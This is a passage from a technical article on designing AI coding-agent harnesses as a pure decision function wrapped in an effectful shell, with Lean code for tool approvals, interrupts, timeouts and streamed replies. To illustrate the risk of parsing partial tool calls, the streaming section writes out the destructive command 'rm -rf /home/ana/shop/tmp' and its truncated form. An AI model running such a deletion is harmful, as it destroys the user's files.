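# Building an AI agent as a pure decision core with an effectful shell

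## What does an agent program do, and why separate its decisions from its effects?

An AI agent is a program that works through a task by calling a language model repeatedly and acting on the replies. The model takes text and returns text, which may include a tool call, a structured request such as "run the tests" or "replace these lines in this file". The program around the model, called the harness, builds the model's input, executes its tool calls and returns the results to it. The model executes nothing itself. OpenAI's Codex and Anthropic's Claude Code are harnesses for programming work.

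A harness decides things, such as whether a call may run or whether to retry a failed one, and it acts on files, processes, networks and the screen. Programmers can write both into one loop, or they can put the decisions in a small function that touches nothing outside itself (the core) and the actions in a layer around it (the shell). Separating them lets programmers test the core without a network or a disk and, in a suitable language, prove theorems about it.

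### The agent loop

Bolin (2026), in *Unrolling the Codex agent loop*, follows one request through Codex. A user asks for an architecture diagram in a project's README file. The harness sends the model this request along with standing instructions and a list of available tools. The model's reply contains a tool call, a command line that prints the README. The harness runs the command, appends the call and its output to the conversation, and sends the whole conversation back to the model. This repeats until the model replies with only a message for the user, which ends the turn. A single turn can contain hundreds of tool calls.

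UT Austin's autumn 2026 course slides, *Coding agent fundamentals*, divide a coding agent's work among three software layers. The model chooses the next step, the harness checks policy and routes the call, and the operating system runs the process. Nothing changes on disk until the harness runs the tool. In one example, a single prompt leads to six child processes, including a text search, a type checker and two test runs.

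Any safeguard against a bad proposal therefore has to be in the harness or below it. Raschka's *Components of A Coding Agent* lists the checks that a harness can make before a tool runs: whether the tool exists, whether its arguments are valid, whether the user must approve, and whether the file path is inside the project. Other decisions in the harness affect how well the agent works. UT Austin cites an experiment in which the software company LangChain changed only the harness and kept the same model. The score on Terminal-Bench 2.0, a set of 89 terminal tasks, rose from 52.8 to 66.5. The changes included a detector for repeated command lines and a rule that the agent must run a verification before declaring itself done.

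### One loop that does everything

Here is a small harness with a permission check, retries, process calls and screen updates in one loop.

```
history = [request]
while True:
    reply = ask_model(history)                # network
    history.append(reply)
    if not reply.calls: break
    for call in reply.calls:
        if not user_approves(call): continue  # permission check
        for attempt in range(3):              # retries
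            result = run_process(call)        # starts a program
            screen.show(result)               # display
            if result.ok: break
            call = ask_model(history + [result]).calls[0]  # corrected call
        history.append(result)
```

The programmer wants nothing to run without approval, so the code checks for approval just before the retry loop. If the user approves a test run and it fails, the harness asks the model for a corrected call and runs that call without the user's approval. The new call may only correct a misspelt option, or it may delete a directory before running the tests.

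Retry limits of this sort are ordinary practice. Dex (2025), in *12 Factor Agents*, a guide from the company HumanLayer, suggests stopping after about three attempts at a tool and keeps the error counter inside the loop. (In Dex's code a corrected call goes round the whole loop again, so this particular hole does not open.)

To catch the mistake by testing, someone has to write stand-ins for the model, the user and the process runner, and then think of the case, among a great many, in which the first run fails and the second call differs from the first. In *Boundaries*, a 2012 talk on software design and testing, Bernhardt estimates that a program with n branches has roughly 2^n paths, which for 500 branches is a number with about 150 digits. In the loop above, one call can end in five ways: refusal, success on the first, second or third attempt, or three failures. Ten calls in a turn give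 5^10 combinations, nearly ten million. Bernhardt also points out that if the stand-ins stop matching the real components, the tests keep passing while the production system is broken.

Proving a theorem about this loop is harder still, because it would require a mathematical model of `run_process`, and therefore of the operating system, as well as of the user, the network and the screen. Proving that "nothing runs" would also mean checking every line of the program that could start a process, including `screen.show` if it opens long output in a separate pager program.

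### The step function

A pure function computes a result that depends only on its arguments, and does nothing else. Addition is pure. An effect is anything a program does beyond computing a value, such as reading the clock, writing a file, starting a process, calling a network service, or drawing on the screen. Reading counts as an effect because a function that reads the clock, for example, can return different results for the same arguments.

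A state machine consists of a set of states, a starting state, and a rule that gives the next state for each state and input. The core of an agent is a state machine whose rule is a pure function with this signature:

```
step : State × Event → State × List Command
```

*step* takes a state and an event, and returns a state and a list of commands, which may be empty. The state holds whatever the agent must carry forward, such as the conversation so far, the calls that await approval and the number of failed attempts. An event is a data value that records something that happened, such as the model replying, the user pressing "yes" or a process exiting with code 1. A command is a data value that describes an effect for the shell to carry out. The command `Run("pytest")` is only a record, so creating it does not start a process.

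The shell does the rest, and its main loop is short.

```
while True:
    event = next_event()
    state, commands = step(state, event)
    for c in commands: perform(c)    # the outcome returns later as an event
```

This shell is unrelated to the Unix shell, the program that runs typed command lines. The interpreter is the part behind `perform` that carries out commands and reports their outcomes as events. *Replay Is a Family of Assertions* (Nakajima, 2026) formalises an agent runtime in which the pure code can request an effect, but only the interpreter can produce the event that reports its outcome. Without this rule, a core could record the success of a test run that never took place.

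The promise about approval now means that whenever `Run(c)` appears in a list that *step* returns, an earlier event approved exactly the call c. To test one case, a programmer builds a state and an event, calls *step* and checks the returned list, without needing any stand-ins. A careless programmer can still make the old mistake by writing a *step* that responds to a corrected call by immediately returning `Run`, but the mistake now shows up in the return value, where a few lines of test code can find it.

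A proof can go further than tests and cover every event in every state the agent can reach, including all ten million combinations. People write such proofs in a proof assistant, a program such as Lean or Rocq that lets them write both code and theorems and checks the proofs mechanically. The trusted base is everything the theorem doesn't cover that must still work correctly for the property to hold in practice. Here it includes the interpreter, the operating system, the compiler and the proof checker itself. For example, if the shell started a process that no command had requested, it would break the promise about approval even though the theorem would still be true.

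### Where the shape comes from

The signature is some seventy years old. Mealy's *A Method for Synthesizing Sequential Circuits* (1955) dealt with switching circuits that have memory, which are far harder to design than simple circuits without it. Chang (1963), in *Automata & Sequential Machines, A Survey*, restates Mealy's definition: the present input and the present state together fix both the present output and the next state. With q for the state and i for the input, that makes two functions:

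```
next state = δ(q, i)
output     = λ(q, i)
```

Combining Mealy's next-state and output functions into one function that returns a pair gives *step*. In E. F. Moore's rival definition, the output depends only on the state. Chang notes that the two definitions can describe the same systems, so the choice is a matter of convenience. Mealy's suits an agent because an agent's commands mostly respond to the latest event. Mealy's machines have finitely many states, but an agent's conversation has no fixed limit on its length, so nobody can check an agent's core by listing all its states.

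Bernhardt named the two parts the "functional core" and "imperative shell", and gave a practical reason for separating them. The talk's example is a billing program that finds subscribers who have not paid for a month and emails them. In the first version, one piece of code queries the database, picks out the late payers and sends the mail. In the second, a pure core takes a list of users and returns those who are late, and a thin shell fetches the list and sends the mail. Bernhardt argues that this does more than cut a method in half, because it puts all the decisions on one side and all the dependencies on the other. The core has many paths but few dependencies, so it suits fast isolated tests. The shell depends on much more, but has so few paths that a handful of slow tests of the whole system is enough. An earlier screencast from Bernhardt's company, Destroy All Software, applied the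 same division to a Twitter client, whose core handled the timelines and cursor positions while the shell handled the terminal, the database and the network.

In the billing program, however, the core returns a list of people, and it is the shell's code that says they should get an email. Elm, a language for web interfaces, moved that knowledge into the returned data. Lloyd (2016), in *Functional Event Sourcing meets The Elm Architecture*, credits Elm's designer Evan Czaplicki with a drastic simplification that year, which removed the "signals" on which earlier designs of this family relied heavily. The University of Chicago's *Introduction to MVC in Elm* distinguishes two versions of what remained. In the simpler one, a function called `update` takes a message and a state and returns a state. The fuller one adds commands, and an older Elm guide, *The Elm Architecture + Effects*, gives its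 type:

```
update : Msg -> Model -> (Model, Cmd Msg)
```

In Elm, a `Msg` is an event, and the `Model` is the program's state, not a language model. Elm's runtime, which is the same for every Elm program, acts as the shell. According to Elm's *Commands and Subscriptions*, it turns clicks into messages and carries out the commands that the program returns, such as an HTTP request. A program has to return a command even to get a random number, because a pure function cannot produce randomness.

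The Decider pattern comes from event sourcing, in which a program keeps an ordered log of what happened and recomputes the current state from it. The EquinoxJS library page *Decider* credits Jérémie Chassaing with the best account of the pattern and illustrates it with a counter that must stay between 0 and 10. One function, `decide`, takes a request and the current state and returns a list of facts. Another, `evolve`, takes a state and one fact and returns the next state. If the counter is at 10, a request to increment it must not produce the fact "incremented". The terms can be confusing, because the pattern calls the incoming request a "command" and the resulting fact an "event". Hackage's *Crem.Decider* describes a Decider as a Mealy machine that computes its next state from the previous state and the output. The pattern therefore added the ability to rebuild the state from saved outputs.

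HumanLayer's guide applied the idea to agents. Its twelfth rule, which Dex offers "mostly just for fun", is "Make Your Agent a Stateless Reducer". A reducer is a function that folds a list of events into a state one event at a time. The more substantial eighth rule is that a program should be able to pause after the model selects a tool and before the tool runs. Otherwise, Dex argues, developers must keep the whole process in memory while a person decides, limit the agent to harmless tools, or give it dangerous ones and hope nothing goes wrong. A program built around *step* needs no extra mechanism to pause, since the proposed call stays in the state until an event brings the user's answer.

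Vel's *Factor 12*, the documentation of an agent library, provides working code. Its reducer takes a state and an event and returns a new state and a list of effects (called commands above). There are three kinds of effect: call the model, call a tool, and halt. Vel uses the reducer only when replies arrive whole rather than as a stream. Nakajima writes the signature as S × E → S × F* and also treats it as an established pattern, tracing it to Mealy, Elm and the Decider.

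### The model stays outside the core

In Vel's list, calling the model is one effect among others. The core returns a command containing the conversation, the interpreter sends the conversation over the network, and the reply comes back as an event, as random numbers do in Elm. The model may give different replies to the same conversation, but the core is still deterministic because it returns the same new state and commands whenever it receives the same state and reply. If the log holds the replies, folding a pure function over it gives the same state every time. Nakajima states this as a proposition without proof and calls it the trivial base case because it leaves open whether the events could have arrived in another order and whether it is safe to repeat the effects.

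With this arrangement, a theorem about *step* also needs no assumptions about the model. It covers every possible event and so every possible reply, whether it comes from a good model, a confused one, or one that has followed hostile instructions hidden in a web page. Developers can therefore replace the model and keep the proof. But the theorem doesn't establish whether a proposal was wise. The theorem about approval still holds when the user trusts the model's explanation and approves deleting the wrong directory.

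## How does a pure core run a coding task, step by step?

In a Python project, the function `total` in `cart.py` should add up a list of prices. Its test expects `total([2, 3])` to return 5 but gets 6, because the function computes `sum(prices, 1)`, which starts the sum at 1. A user asks an agent to fix the bug.

The agent can read a file, replace text in a file, or run the tests. Reads run at once, while edits and test runs wait for the user's approval. Test runs need approval because they execute whatever code is in the project, including anything the model has just written. The agent can run tools up to five times in total, and its fuel is the number of runs it has left.

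### State, events and commands

The code below is close to Lean. `inductive` lists the forms a value can take, `structure` groups named fields, `Nat` is a whole number from 0 up, and an `Option` is either `none` or `some` value.

```lean
inductive Tool
  | read (path : String)
  | edit (path old new : String)
  | test

inductive Status
  | waiting | running | finished

structure State where
  calls  : Nat → Option (Tool × Status)    -- the table of calls, by id
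  nextId : Nat                             -- the next unused id
  fuel   : Nat                             -- tool runs left

inductive Event
  | ModelReplied (call : Option Tool)      -- none: a closing message
  | Approved (id : Nat)
  | Denied (id : Nat)
  | ToolFinished (id : Nat) (output : String)
  | Interrupted

inductive Command
  | AskModel (text : String)
  | AskUser (id : Nat) (tool : Tool)
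  | RunTool (id : Nat) (tool : Tool)
  | Kill (id : Nat)
```

A call's status is one value with three possible forms. With two yes-or-no fields, `isWaiting` and `isRunning`, a call could be marked as both waiting and running. Mermaid-cli, an open-source coding agent in Rust, originally used such fields, including `is_generating` and `is_cancelling`. According to its *state.rs*, only convention kept them consistent, so the new version lists the possible states explicitly.

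The core assigns the ids. A model's reply often includes an id, but mermaid-cli treats it as optional and stores it beside a number from its own counter. `Approved` contains only an id, and the tool that runs is the one already in the table, so an approval can't substitute a different call.

`State` omits the conversation to keep the example short. None of the rules depends on the conversation, so in this example the interpreter stores it, appends the text of each `AskModel`, and sends the whole conversation to the model.

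### The step function

Two small helpers come first. `put` records a call in the table, and `launch` starts a tool if there is fuel.

```lean
def State.put (s : State) (id : Nat) (t : Tool) (st : Status) : State :=
  { s with calls := fun n => if n = id then some (t, st) else s.calls n }

def launch (s : State) (id : Nat) (t : Tool) : State × List Command :=
  match s.fuel with
  | 0     => (s.put id t .finished, [])
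  | f + 1 => ({ s.put id t .running with fuel := f }, [.RunTool id t])

def step (s : State) : Event → State × List Command
  | .ModelReplied none => (s, [])
  | .ModelReplied (some t) =>
      let id := s.nextId
      let s  := { s with nextId := id + 1 }
      match t with
      | .read _ => launch s id t
      | _       => (s.put id t .waiting, [.AskUser id t])
  | .Approved id =>
      match s.calls id with
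      | some (t, .waiting) => launch s id t
      | _                  => (s, [])
  | .Denied id =>
      match s.calls id with
      | some (t, .waiting) =>
          (s.put id t .finished, [.AskModel "The user refused."])
      | _ => (s, [])
  | .ToolFinished id output =>
      match s.calls id with
      | some (t, .running) => (s.put id t .finished, [.AskModel output])
      | _                  => (s, [])
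  | .Interrupted =>
      let kill := fun id => match s.calls id with
        | some (_, .running) => some (Command.Kill id)
        | _                  => none
      ({ s with calls := fun n =>
           (s.calls n).map fun (t, _) => (t, Status.finished) },
       (List.range s.nextId).filterMap kill)
```

Only `launch` creates a `RunTool`, and the same line subtracts a unit of fuel. `step` uses `launch` in two places: when the model proposes a read, and when the user approves a waiting call. A corrected call arrives as a new `ModelReplied`, gets a new id and waits for its own approval, whereas the single-loop harness described earlier ran corrected calls under the old approval.

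When the fuel runs out, `launch` marks the call as finished and returns no commands, so the agent stops. It doesn't send the model a note about the limit, though that would be friendlier, because a model that kept proposing reads could then keep the loop going forever, with another model call each time. In the version above, `step` calls the model again only after a tool run or a refusal, so a run makes at most six model calls (the first one and one for each tool run), plus one for each time the user refuses.

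`Interrupted` closes every call and returns a `Kill` for each one that was running. A killed process may still deliver output, but `step` ignores it because its call is already closed. However, the state doesn't record which request a model reply belongs to, so a reply already on its way when the user interrupts will still open a new call, and if that call is a read, it will run. mermaid-cli's *Mermaid Architecture (v0.7+)* solves this by putting a turn number in every event that carries the result of an effect and dropping events whose number doesn't match the current turn.

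### The interpreter

Written out for this example, the shell's main loop has one case for each kind of command.

```lean
partial def run (s : State) (commands : List Command) : IO Unit := do
  for c in commands do
    match c with
    | .AskModel text => spawn (askModel text)   -- later: ModelReplied
    | .AskUser id t  => spawn (askUser id t)    -- later: Approved or Denied
    | .RunTool id t  => spawn (runTool id t)    -- later: ToolFinished
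    | .Kill id       => killProcess id
  let event ← nextEvent
  let (s', commands') := step s event
  run s' commands'
```

`spawn` runs a job in the background and puts the event the job returns into a queue. `nextEvent` takes the oldest event from the queue, or waits for one. If the user presses Escape, `Interrupted` goes into the same queue. The Lean keyword `partial` marks the function as one that may never end.

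`IO` in the type of `run` marks code that may have effects. The type of `step` has no `IO`, so Lean rejects a file read inside `step` unless the programmer uses deliberately unsafe code. Most agent libraries with this design are written in Rust, Clojure or TypeScript, which have no such check, so programmers have to keep the core pure themselves.

A working agent's loop isn't much longer. The one in mermaid-cli has about 40 lines. It draws the screen from the state, then waits for the result of an effect, a key press, an operating system signal or a clock tick (60 per second), whichever comes first. Then it calls its step function, `update`, and dispatches the commands. Its set of commands is much larger than the example's, with twenty kinds instead of four. They include reading the clipboard, setting the terminal window's title and saving the conversation.

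### One run from start to finish

The shell starts the agent by calling `run` with an empty table, next id 1, fuel 5 and a single `AskModel` containing the user's request. Each row of the table below shows what `step` returns for one event.

| | Event | New state | Commands |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `ModelReplied` (read `cart.py`) | call 1 running; next id 2; fuel 4 | `RunTool 1` (read) |
| 2 | `ToolFinished 1` (text of the file) | call 1 finished; next id 2; fuel 4 | `AskModel` (text of the file) |
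| 3 | `ModelReplied` (edit: `sum(prices, 1)` becomes `sum(prices)`) | call 2 waiting; next id 3; fuel 4 | `AskUser 2` (edit) |
| 4 | `Approved 2` | call 2 running; next id 3; fuel 3 | `RunTool 2` (edit) |
| 5 | `ToolFinished 2` ("1 replacement") | call 2 finished; next id 3; fuel 3 | `AskModel` ("1 replacement") |
| 6 | `ModelReplied` (run the tests) | call 3 waiting; next id 4; fuel 3 | `AskUser 3` (test) |
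| 7 | `Approved 3` | call 3 running; next id 4; fuel 2 | `RunTool 3` (test) |
| 8 | `ToolFinished 3` ("1 passed") | call 3 finished; next id 4; fuel 2 | `AskModel` ("1 passed") |
| 9 | `ModelReplied` (no call) | no change | none |

The file on disk changes between rows 4 and 5, while the interpreter carries out `RunTool 2`. After row 9, the loop waits for another event. A full harness would then accept the user's next message as a sixth kind of event.

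The core doesn't check whether the tests passed. If the result in row 8 had been "1 failed", `step` would have passed that text to the model in the same way, and the model could still have sent its closing message. To let the agent finish only after a passing test run, a programmer would add that rule to the first branch of `step`, which handles the closing message. The state would need a new field for the last test result, and `ToolFinished` would need to carry the exit code, because a test can itself print text such as "1 passed".

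### A second approval for the same call

Suppose the user presses "y" twice, and the second press arrives just after row 4. `step` looks up call 2, finds that it is running, and takes the last line of the `Approved` branch.

```lean
step s (.Approved 2) = (s, [])
```

The state stays the same and the core returns no command. The same happens if the second press arrives after the edit has finished, if the user has already refused the call, or if the id never existed. Repeating this edit would do little harm, because the text `sum(prices, 1)` is no longer in the file. But a second test run would waste time and a unit of fuel, and a tool that posts a comment or pays an invoice would do so twice.

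The protection works because a single call to `step` both checks the status and changes it. In a harness with two threads, both could read "waiting" before either wrote "running", and both would start the tool. The loop above avoids this by handling one event at a time and always passing in the latest state. But if a shell called `step` twice with the same old state, it would get two `RunTool` commands, and no code inside `step` could prevent that. Outskirts Labs' *ol.llx.agent.driver*, from the documentation of a Clojure agent library, makes the precaution an explicit rule that only the driver loop may call `step` or change the state. The functions that carry out effects may only read the state.

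### Testing with plain values

These lines test the double approval.

```lean
def s0 : State := { calls := fun _ => none, nextId := 1, fuel := 5 }
def s1 := (step s0 (.ModelReplied (some .test))).1    -- call 1 waiting
def s2 := (step s1 (.Approved 1)).1                   -- call 1 running

example : (step s1 (.Approved 1)).2 = [.RunTool 1 .test] := rfl
example : (step s2 (.Approved 1)).2 = []                 := rfl
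example : (step s2 (.Approved 7)).2 = []                 := rfl
example : s2.fuel = 4                                    := rfl
```

With `rfl`, Lean computes the left side and checks that it equals the right. If the check fails, the file doesn't compile. The tests don't start any processes or wait for anything.

mermaid-cli's test file works the same way on a larger core. One test sends a second cancel request while the first is in progress and checks that the core returns no second cancel command. Another test covers multiple tool requests in one reply, which mermaid-cli allows but the example leaves out. It sets up two running calls and delivers the first result, after which the command list must be empty. After the second result arrives, the list must contain a call to the model. The data type helps enforce this order by giving every call a slot for its result, and the core can continue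 only through a function that succeeds once all the slots are full.

Tests like these can still miss a case that nobody thought of. According to a comment in the same file, version 0.7.0, the first with the pure core, shipped with a bug where the model requested a tool and nothing happened. The test that now guards against it needs only three events. Another comment says that the core had no branch for the event that ends a cancelled turn, so the screen stayed on "cancelling" until an error message arrived from the abandoned model request, which didn't always happen. When someone writes a test's events by hand, they can easily include one that the real shell never sends, and the test then passes even though the program hangs for users.

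A computer can also search the event sequences automatically. Stately's *Testing and verification* describes such a search in an agent package for XState, a state-machine library. The search tries every choice the model could make and every outside event, without calling a model. By default it stops after eight branch points on a path, 200 finished paths or 100,000 branch points in total. In one example, a machine that handles refunds must never reach a state called `illegallyIssued`. The search tries five amounts (0, 1, 100, 100.01 and 500), combined with an order lookup that succeeds, finds nothing or fails. If the search finds no path to the forbidden state and no limit cut it short, Stately counts the result as a proof. Strictly, the proof covers only those five amounts. It extends to all amounts only if the programmer picked values on both sides of every threshold in the code, so that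 any amount in between takes a branch the search has already tried.

The default settings would also miss the double approval, because they deliver outside events only when the machine is idle, and the second "y" arrives while a tool is running. To make the search try events while a tool is running, a programmer has to set `interleave: "pending"`.

The shell still needs its own tests, and these do require stand-ins. For this purpose, ralph-workflow, a Rust program that leads coding agents through development and review in a git repository, supplies an in-memory file system and a mock process runner. Stately's *Evals* describes two ways to replace the model. Using a plain function tests the machine alone, while mocking the model provider also tests the code that builds the prompt and parses the reply.

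### What agent libraries put in the core

Several open-source projects have built agents this way. Outskirts Labs describes its Clojure library *ol.llx* as experimental, and version 2.0 of Stately's package is in alpha. CodeSwarm is a terminal program in which coding agents such as Claude Code and Codex take turns on one task. All three follow the principle that the core should do no input or output, but they differ considerably in what they include in the core.

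| Project | Form of the core | Decided in the core | Left outside |
|---|---|---|---|
| Outskirts Labs | `step` takes a state and an input, and returns a state and effects | the phase (idle, streaming, running tools or closed) and when to call the model or a tool | trimming the conversation, the tools' own code |
| ralph-workflow | `reduce` returns the next state, and `determine_next_effect` reads the effect off it | the phase of work, which agent to use, what to do when one fails | the tool calls that each agent makes |
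| CodeSwarm | `reduce` applies one event, and effects stand for input, output and drawing | how each event changes the session | running the agents and their tools |
| Stately | a transition function takes a snapshot and an event, and returns a snapshot and actions | which events are legal in each state | storage, retries, queues, the connection to the model |

ralph-workflow is the odd one out, because its effects depend on the state alone. In the terms of the 1950s that makes it a Moore machine, where the example is a Mealy machine. To rewrite the example this way, a programmer would add a fourth status, "approved". `Approved 2` would only change the status of call 2, and a second function would look at the new state and return `RunTool 2`. The attraction is that a saved state is enough to work out what to do next after a restart. The drawback is that the effect remains due until some event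 changes the state. If the shell runs the edit and fails to report it, the function returns `RunTool 2` again. ralph-workflow also produces one effect at a time, whereas a core that returns a list can start several tools together.

In ralph-workflow, an effect performs a single operation and may not include a retry or a policy decision. In the worked example, if the interpreter ran a failed test command three times within one effect, the core would deduct one unit of fuel for three runs, and the limit of five would in practice be a limit of fifteen. Some projects don't follow this rule. mermaid-cli wraps retries around the code that carries out commands, so adapters don't each have to implement them, and Stately leaves retries to the surrounding program. This is convenient when a network connection drops, but a limit in the core then counts how often the core requests an effect, not how often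 the effect is attempted.

The libraries differ most from the example in how they handle approval. Outskirts Labs' core has four phases and four kinds of effect, but none of them is for requesting permission or waiting for the user's answer. Each tool has its own `execute` function, so the obvious place to add an approval prompt is inside that function, where tests of the core can't check it. CodeSwarm allows tool requests without confirmation by default. Users can choose a stricter policy, which CodeSwarm translates into each agent's permission settings for the agent's harness to enforce. mermaid-cli ran everything without asking until version 0.8. Version 0.9 asks by default before changing files, running commands or taking network actions.

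Stately's package lets the model choose among events, so the model could choose the event that means "approved", a problem the example doesn't have. Developers can mark an event as one that only a person may send, and the package then never offers it to the model. Stately's checker reports an error if a developer lists such an event among the model's options.

Conditions in the machine restrict the model's choices further. In Stately's *You already have an agent workflow*, one model writes a haiku and another judges it, either approving it or asking for a revision. After three revisions, another revision request is illegal, so the package rejects it and asks the judge again. If the judge still doesn't approve, the machine runs out of retries and sends the haiku anyway. The limit caps the number of revisions, but it also means the judge can't block a bad haiku. A machine that handled code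 edits by the same rules would apply a change even if the reviewer had rejected it every time.

The amount of work in a single command also limits what can be proved about an agent. `RunTool` in the example is one read, one edit or one test run. In ralph-workflow and CodeSwarm, a single command can start an entire coding agent, which may read and change dozens of files before it reports back. CodeSwarm has a limit much like fuel, 100 automated turns by default, but a turn can contain any number of tool calls. A theorem about such a core could establish which agent works when, and how often, but nothing about individual edits.

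The projects also differ in which part prepares the text the model sees. In mermaid-cli, the core builds the whole request, including the messages, the standing instructions and the list of tools. Jidoka's *Runic spine internals* describes a similar choice in an Elixir library, where assembling the prompt is one of two pure steps. In Outskirts Labs' Clojure library, *ol.llx*, the interpreter uses functions supplied by the developer to trim and convert the conversation just before sending it. To check that a secret never reaches the model provider, mermaid-cli's developers can inspect the command the core returns, while a developer using *ol.llx* has to test the shell.

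## How do streams, subprocesses, network calls and the screen reach a pure core?

The worked example treats each model reply and each tool run as a single event. In practice, replies arrive a few characters at a time, test runs print output for minutes before they exit, and connections drop halfway. A core that performs no input or output can still handle all this if the shell reports each occurrence as an event.

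### The precedent in network libraries

Some network protocol programmers have worked this way for about a decade and call it "sans-IO". Sans-I/O, a guide from the Python community, defines a sans-IO library as one that neither performs network input or output nor waits for it. The surrounding program reads bytes from the network and passes them to the library. The library buffers an incomplete message and returns an event, such as "request received", once the message is complete.

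The motive was reuse as much as testing. In 2016 Python had several implementations of almost every common protocol, and they shared almost no code. The asynchronous library aiohttp, for example, couldn't use the HTTP parser in Python's standard library, because that parser made its own socket calls.

Firezone's *sans-IO*, an article from a remote-access software company, extends the idea to time. Any function that needs the current time takes it as an argument. The state machine returns its next deadline, and the event loop sets a timer and calls the state machine again when the deadline passes. A test can therefore check that a connection closes after five idle minutes without waiting five minutes. Firezone also reports two drawbacks. The event loop spins uselessly if the state machine keeps returning a deadline that has already passed. A long sequence of steps is also more tedious to write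 as states than as ordinary code.

A sans-IO library depends on its caller for facts about the outside world. In HTTP/2, a receiver signals the sender when it has room for more data. A message in the Python mailing-list thread *SansIO* points out that the library can do much of this work, but the program must still report how much data it has processed. An agent's core likewise depends on the shell to report that a process has exited.

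### Streamed model replies

A model provider can send a reply in fragments while the model is still producing it. If the shell passes raw fragments to the core and the core parses them, a proof can cover the parsing and show that the tool call that runs is the one the model wrote. The programmer then has to write a parser for each provider's format and prove it correct. If the shell assembles the reply and passes it once, the core stays small, but the parser becomes part of the trusted base, the code assumed correct without proof. A theorem about approval then applies to whatever call the parser produced, even if the parser garbled what the model wrote.

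When tools are enabled, Zero, a coding agent for models that run on the user's own machine, waits for the complete reply before reading it, because the streaming parsers in local model servers split tool calls or lose them between fragments.

The example can display fragments and still take the finished call from a single event. Each model request now gets a number, which `AskModel` includes.

```lean
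structure State where
  ...                        -- calls, nextId and fuel, as before
  nextReq : Nat              -- the next unused request number
  asking  : Option Nat       -- the open request, if any
  draft   : String           -- reply text so far, for the screen

def State.ask (s : State) (text : String) : State × List Command :=
  ({ s with nextReq := s.nextReq + 1, asking := some s.nextReq, draft := "" },
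   [.AskModel s.nextReq text])

-- new branches of step
  | .Fragment req text =>
      if s.asking = some req then ({ s with draft := s.draft ++ text }, [])
      else (s, [])
  | .ModelReplied req call =>
      if s.asking = some req then
        reply { s with asking := none } call   -- the earlier ModelReplied code
      else (s, [])
```

Both outcomes of `Fragment` return an empty list, so no fragment can start a tool, whatever its text. `Interrupted` now also sets `asking` to `none`, so `step` drops a reply that was already on its way. The basic version would have accepted that reply.

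Suppose an agent has a tool that runs shell commands, and the model is writing `rm -rf /home/ana/shop/tmp`, but the fragments received so far end at `/home/ana`. A strict JSON parser rejects the unfinished argument. Some interfaces, however, show a call while it is still arriving, a technique that *The Hitchhiker's Guide to Agentic AI* (2026) describes, so they need a parser that accepts partial JSON. That parser can return `rm -rf /home/ana`, a valid command that would delete the user's home directory. Numbers carry the same risk, since a 1 may be the start of 100.

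*Metis* (Yu, 2026) describes a runtime that assembles each call in full before dispatching it, and settles all the approvals in a reply before starting any of its calls. In the tool-calling setup of *SchemaFill* (2026), no call runs until the model has finished the whole sequence. To save time, *Speculative Interaction Agents* (2026) lets tools that only read start on partial information, while tools with side effects still wait for a final confirmation. Developers label the tools by hand, and if the labels are correct, a wrong guess wastes a read and does no other harm.

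Passing fragments also creates more events. The demonstration agent in BoundaryML's *Event-driven agentic loops* publishes every fragment as an event with a stream id. git-iris, an AI assistant for the version-control program git, attaches the whole text so far to each fragment. A reply of 1,000 four-character fragments then takes about two million characters instead of 4,000, but if a fragment goes missing, the next event restores the full text.

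### Subprocesses

`ToolFinished` carries too little information about a test run. The core should be able to show output while the tests run, stop them after a time limit, and distinguish a normal exit from a kill. In the extended version, `Exited` replaces `ToolFinished`, and `launch` returns a second command, `StartTimer (.limit id) 60000`, which sets a one-minute limit.

```lean
inductive Status
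  | waiting | running | timedOut | cancelled | finished

inductive Timer
  | limit (id : Nat) | retry (req : Nat)

inductive Event
  ...
  | Started    (id : Nat)
  | Output     (id : Nat) (text : String)         -- for the screen only
  | Exited     (id : Nat) (code : Option Nat) (output : String)  -- none: killed
  | TimerFired (t : Timer)

-- new branches of step
  | .Started id =>
      match s.calls id with
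      | some (_, .timedOut) | some (_, .cancelled) => (s, [.Kill id])
      | _ => (s, [])
  | .TimerFired (.limit id) =>
      match s.calls id with
      | some (t, .running) => (s.put id t .timedOut, [.Kill id])
      | _ => (s, [])
  | .Exited id code output =>
      match s.calls id, code with
      | some (t, .running),   _      => (s.put id t .finished).ask output
      | some (t, .timedOut),  some _ => (s.put id t .finished).ask output
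      | some (t, .timedOut),  none   =>
          (s.put id t .finished).ask ("Timed out. " ++ output)
      | some (t, .cancelled), _      => (s.put id t .finished, [])
      | _,                    _      => (s, [])
```

The id ties all these events to one call. When the limit expires, the core marks the call `timedOut` and requests a kill, but it waits for `Exited` before sending the model a result. If the process finished by itself just before the kill, `Exited` contains an exit code and the model gets the ordinary result. The core ignores a timer that fires after its call has ended.

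The interpreter starts processes in the background, so it may carry out `Kill 3` before process 3 exists. The kill then has no effect, and the process starts a moment later. When `Started 3` reaches the core, the call is already `cancelled`, so `step` returns `Kill 3` again.

### An interrupt that races with an exit

Suppose the test run, call 3, finishes just as the user presses Escape. Two background jobs report these events, and `step` processes them in the order they enter the queue. On `Interrupted`, the extended core marks running and timed-out calls as `cancelled`, closes waiting calls, and returns a `Kill` for each call that was running.

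| Order in the queue | Event | New state | Commands |
|---|---|---|---|
| Escape first | `Interrupted` | call 3 cancelled | `Kill 3` |
| | `Exited 3` (code 0, "1 passed") | call 3 finished | none |
| Exit first | `Exited 3` (code 0, "1 passed") | call 3 finished; request 4 open | `AskModel 4` ("1 passed") |
| | `Interrupted` | no open request | none |
| | `ModelReplied 4` (any call) | no change | none |

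If Escape comes first, the exit event arrives after the kill command. The interpreter looks up the process for call 3 and does nothing, because the process has already ended. (It must search by call id, because operating systems reuse process numbers and a kill sent to an old number could end an unrelated program.) Since the call is marked `cancelled`, `step` then closes it and sends nothing to the model. If the exit comes first, the core has already sent the model a request to continue, but the reply no longer matches an open request. In both orders, the agent stops and starts no more tools.

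The id matters most when the user interrupts and immediately gives a new instruction. Suppose the agent then starts another test run as call 4. If the core stored only "the current run", it would count the late "1 passed" from call 3 as the result of call 4 and report to the model that its new code had passed.

The basic version marked interrupted calls as `finished` immediately, which also made late events harmless. But a process can keep changing files after the kill command. With a separate `cancelled` status, the core can hold back new tool calls until the old process has exited. That wait needs a time limit too, because the exit event may never come.

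A cancelled call may still have done its work. If call 3 had been an edit, code 0 would mean that the file had changed despite the interrupt. In Yu's tests of Metis, a tool that wrote to disk and then failed left its partial change in place. Providers may also require a result for every tool call, including cancelled ones, so Yu adds an "interrupted" result wherever one is missing. The example would need one more command to do this, which appends a note to the conversation without sending it. The core could use the exit code to word the note correctly.

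### Network failures, time and chance

A request to the model can fail because the provider is overloaded, the user has exceeded a rate limit, or the connection breaks. If the core handles retries, the shell reports each failure and the core sets the delay before the next attempt.

```lean
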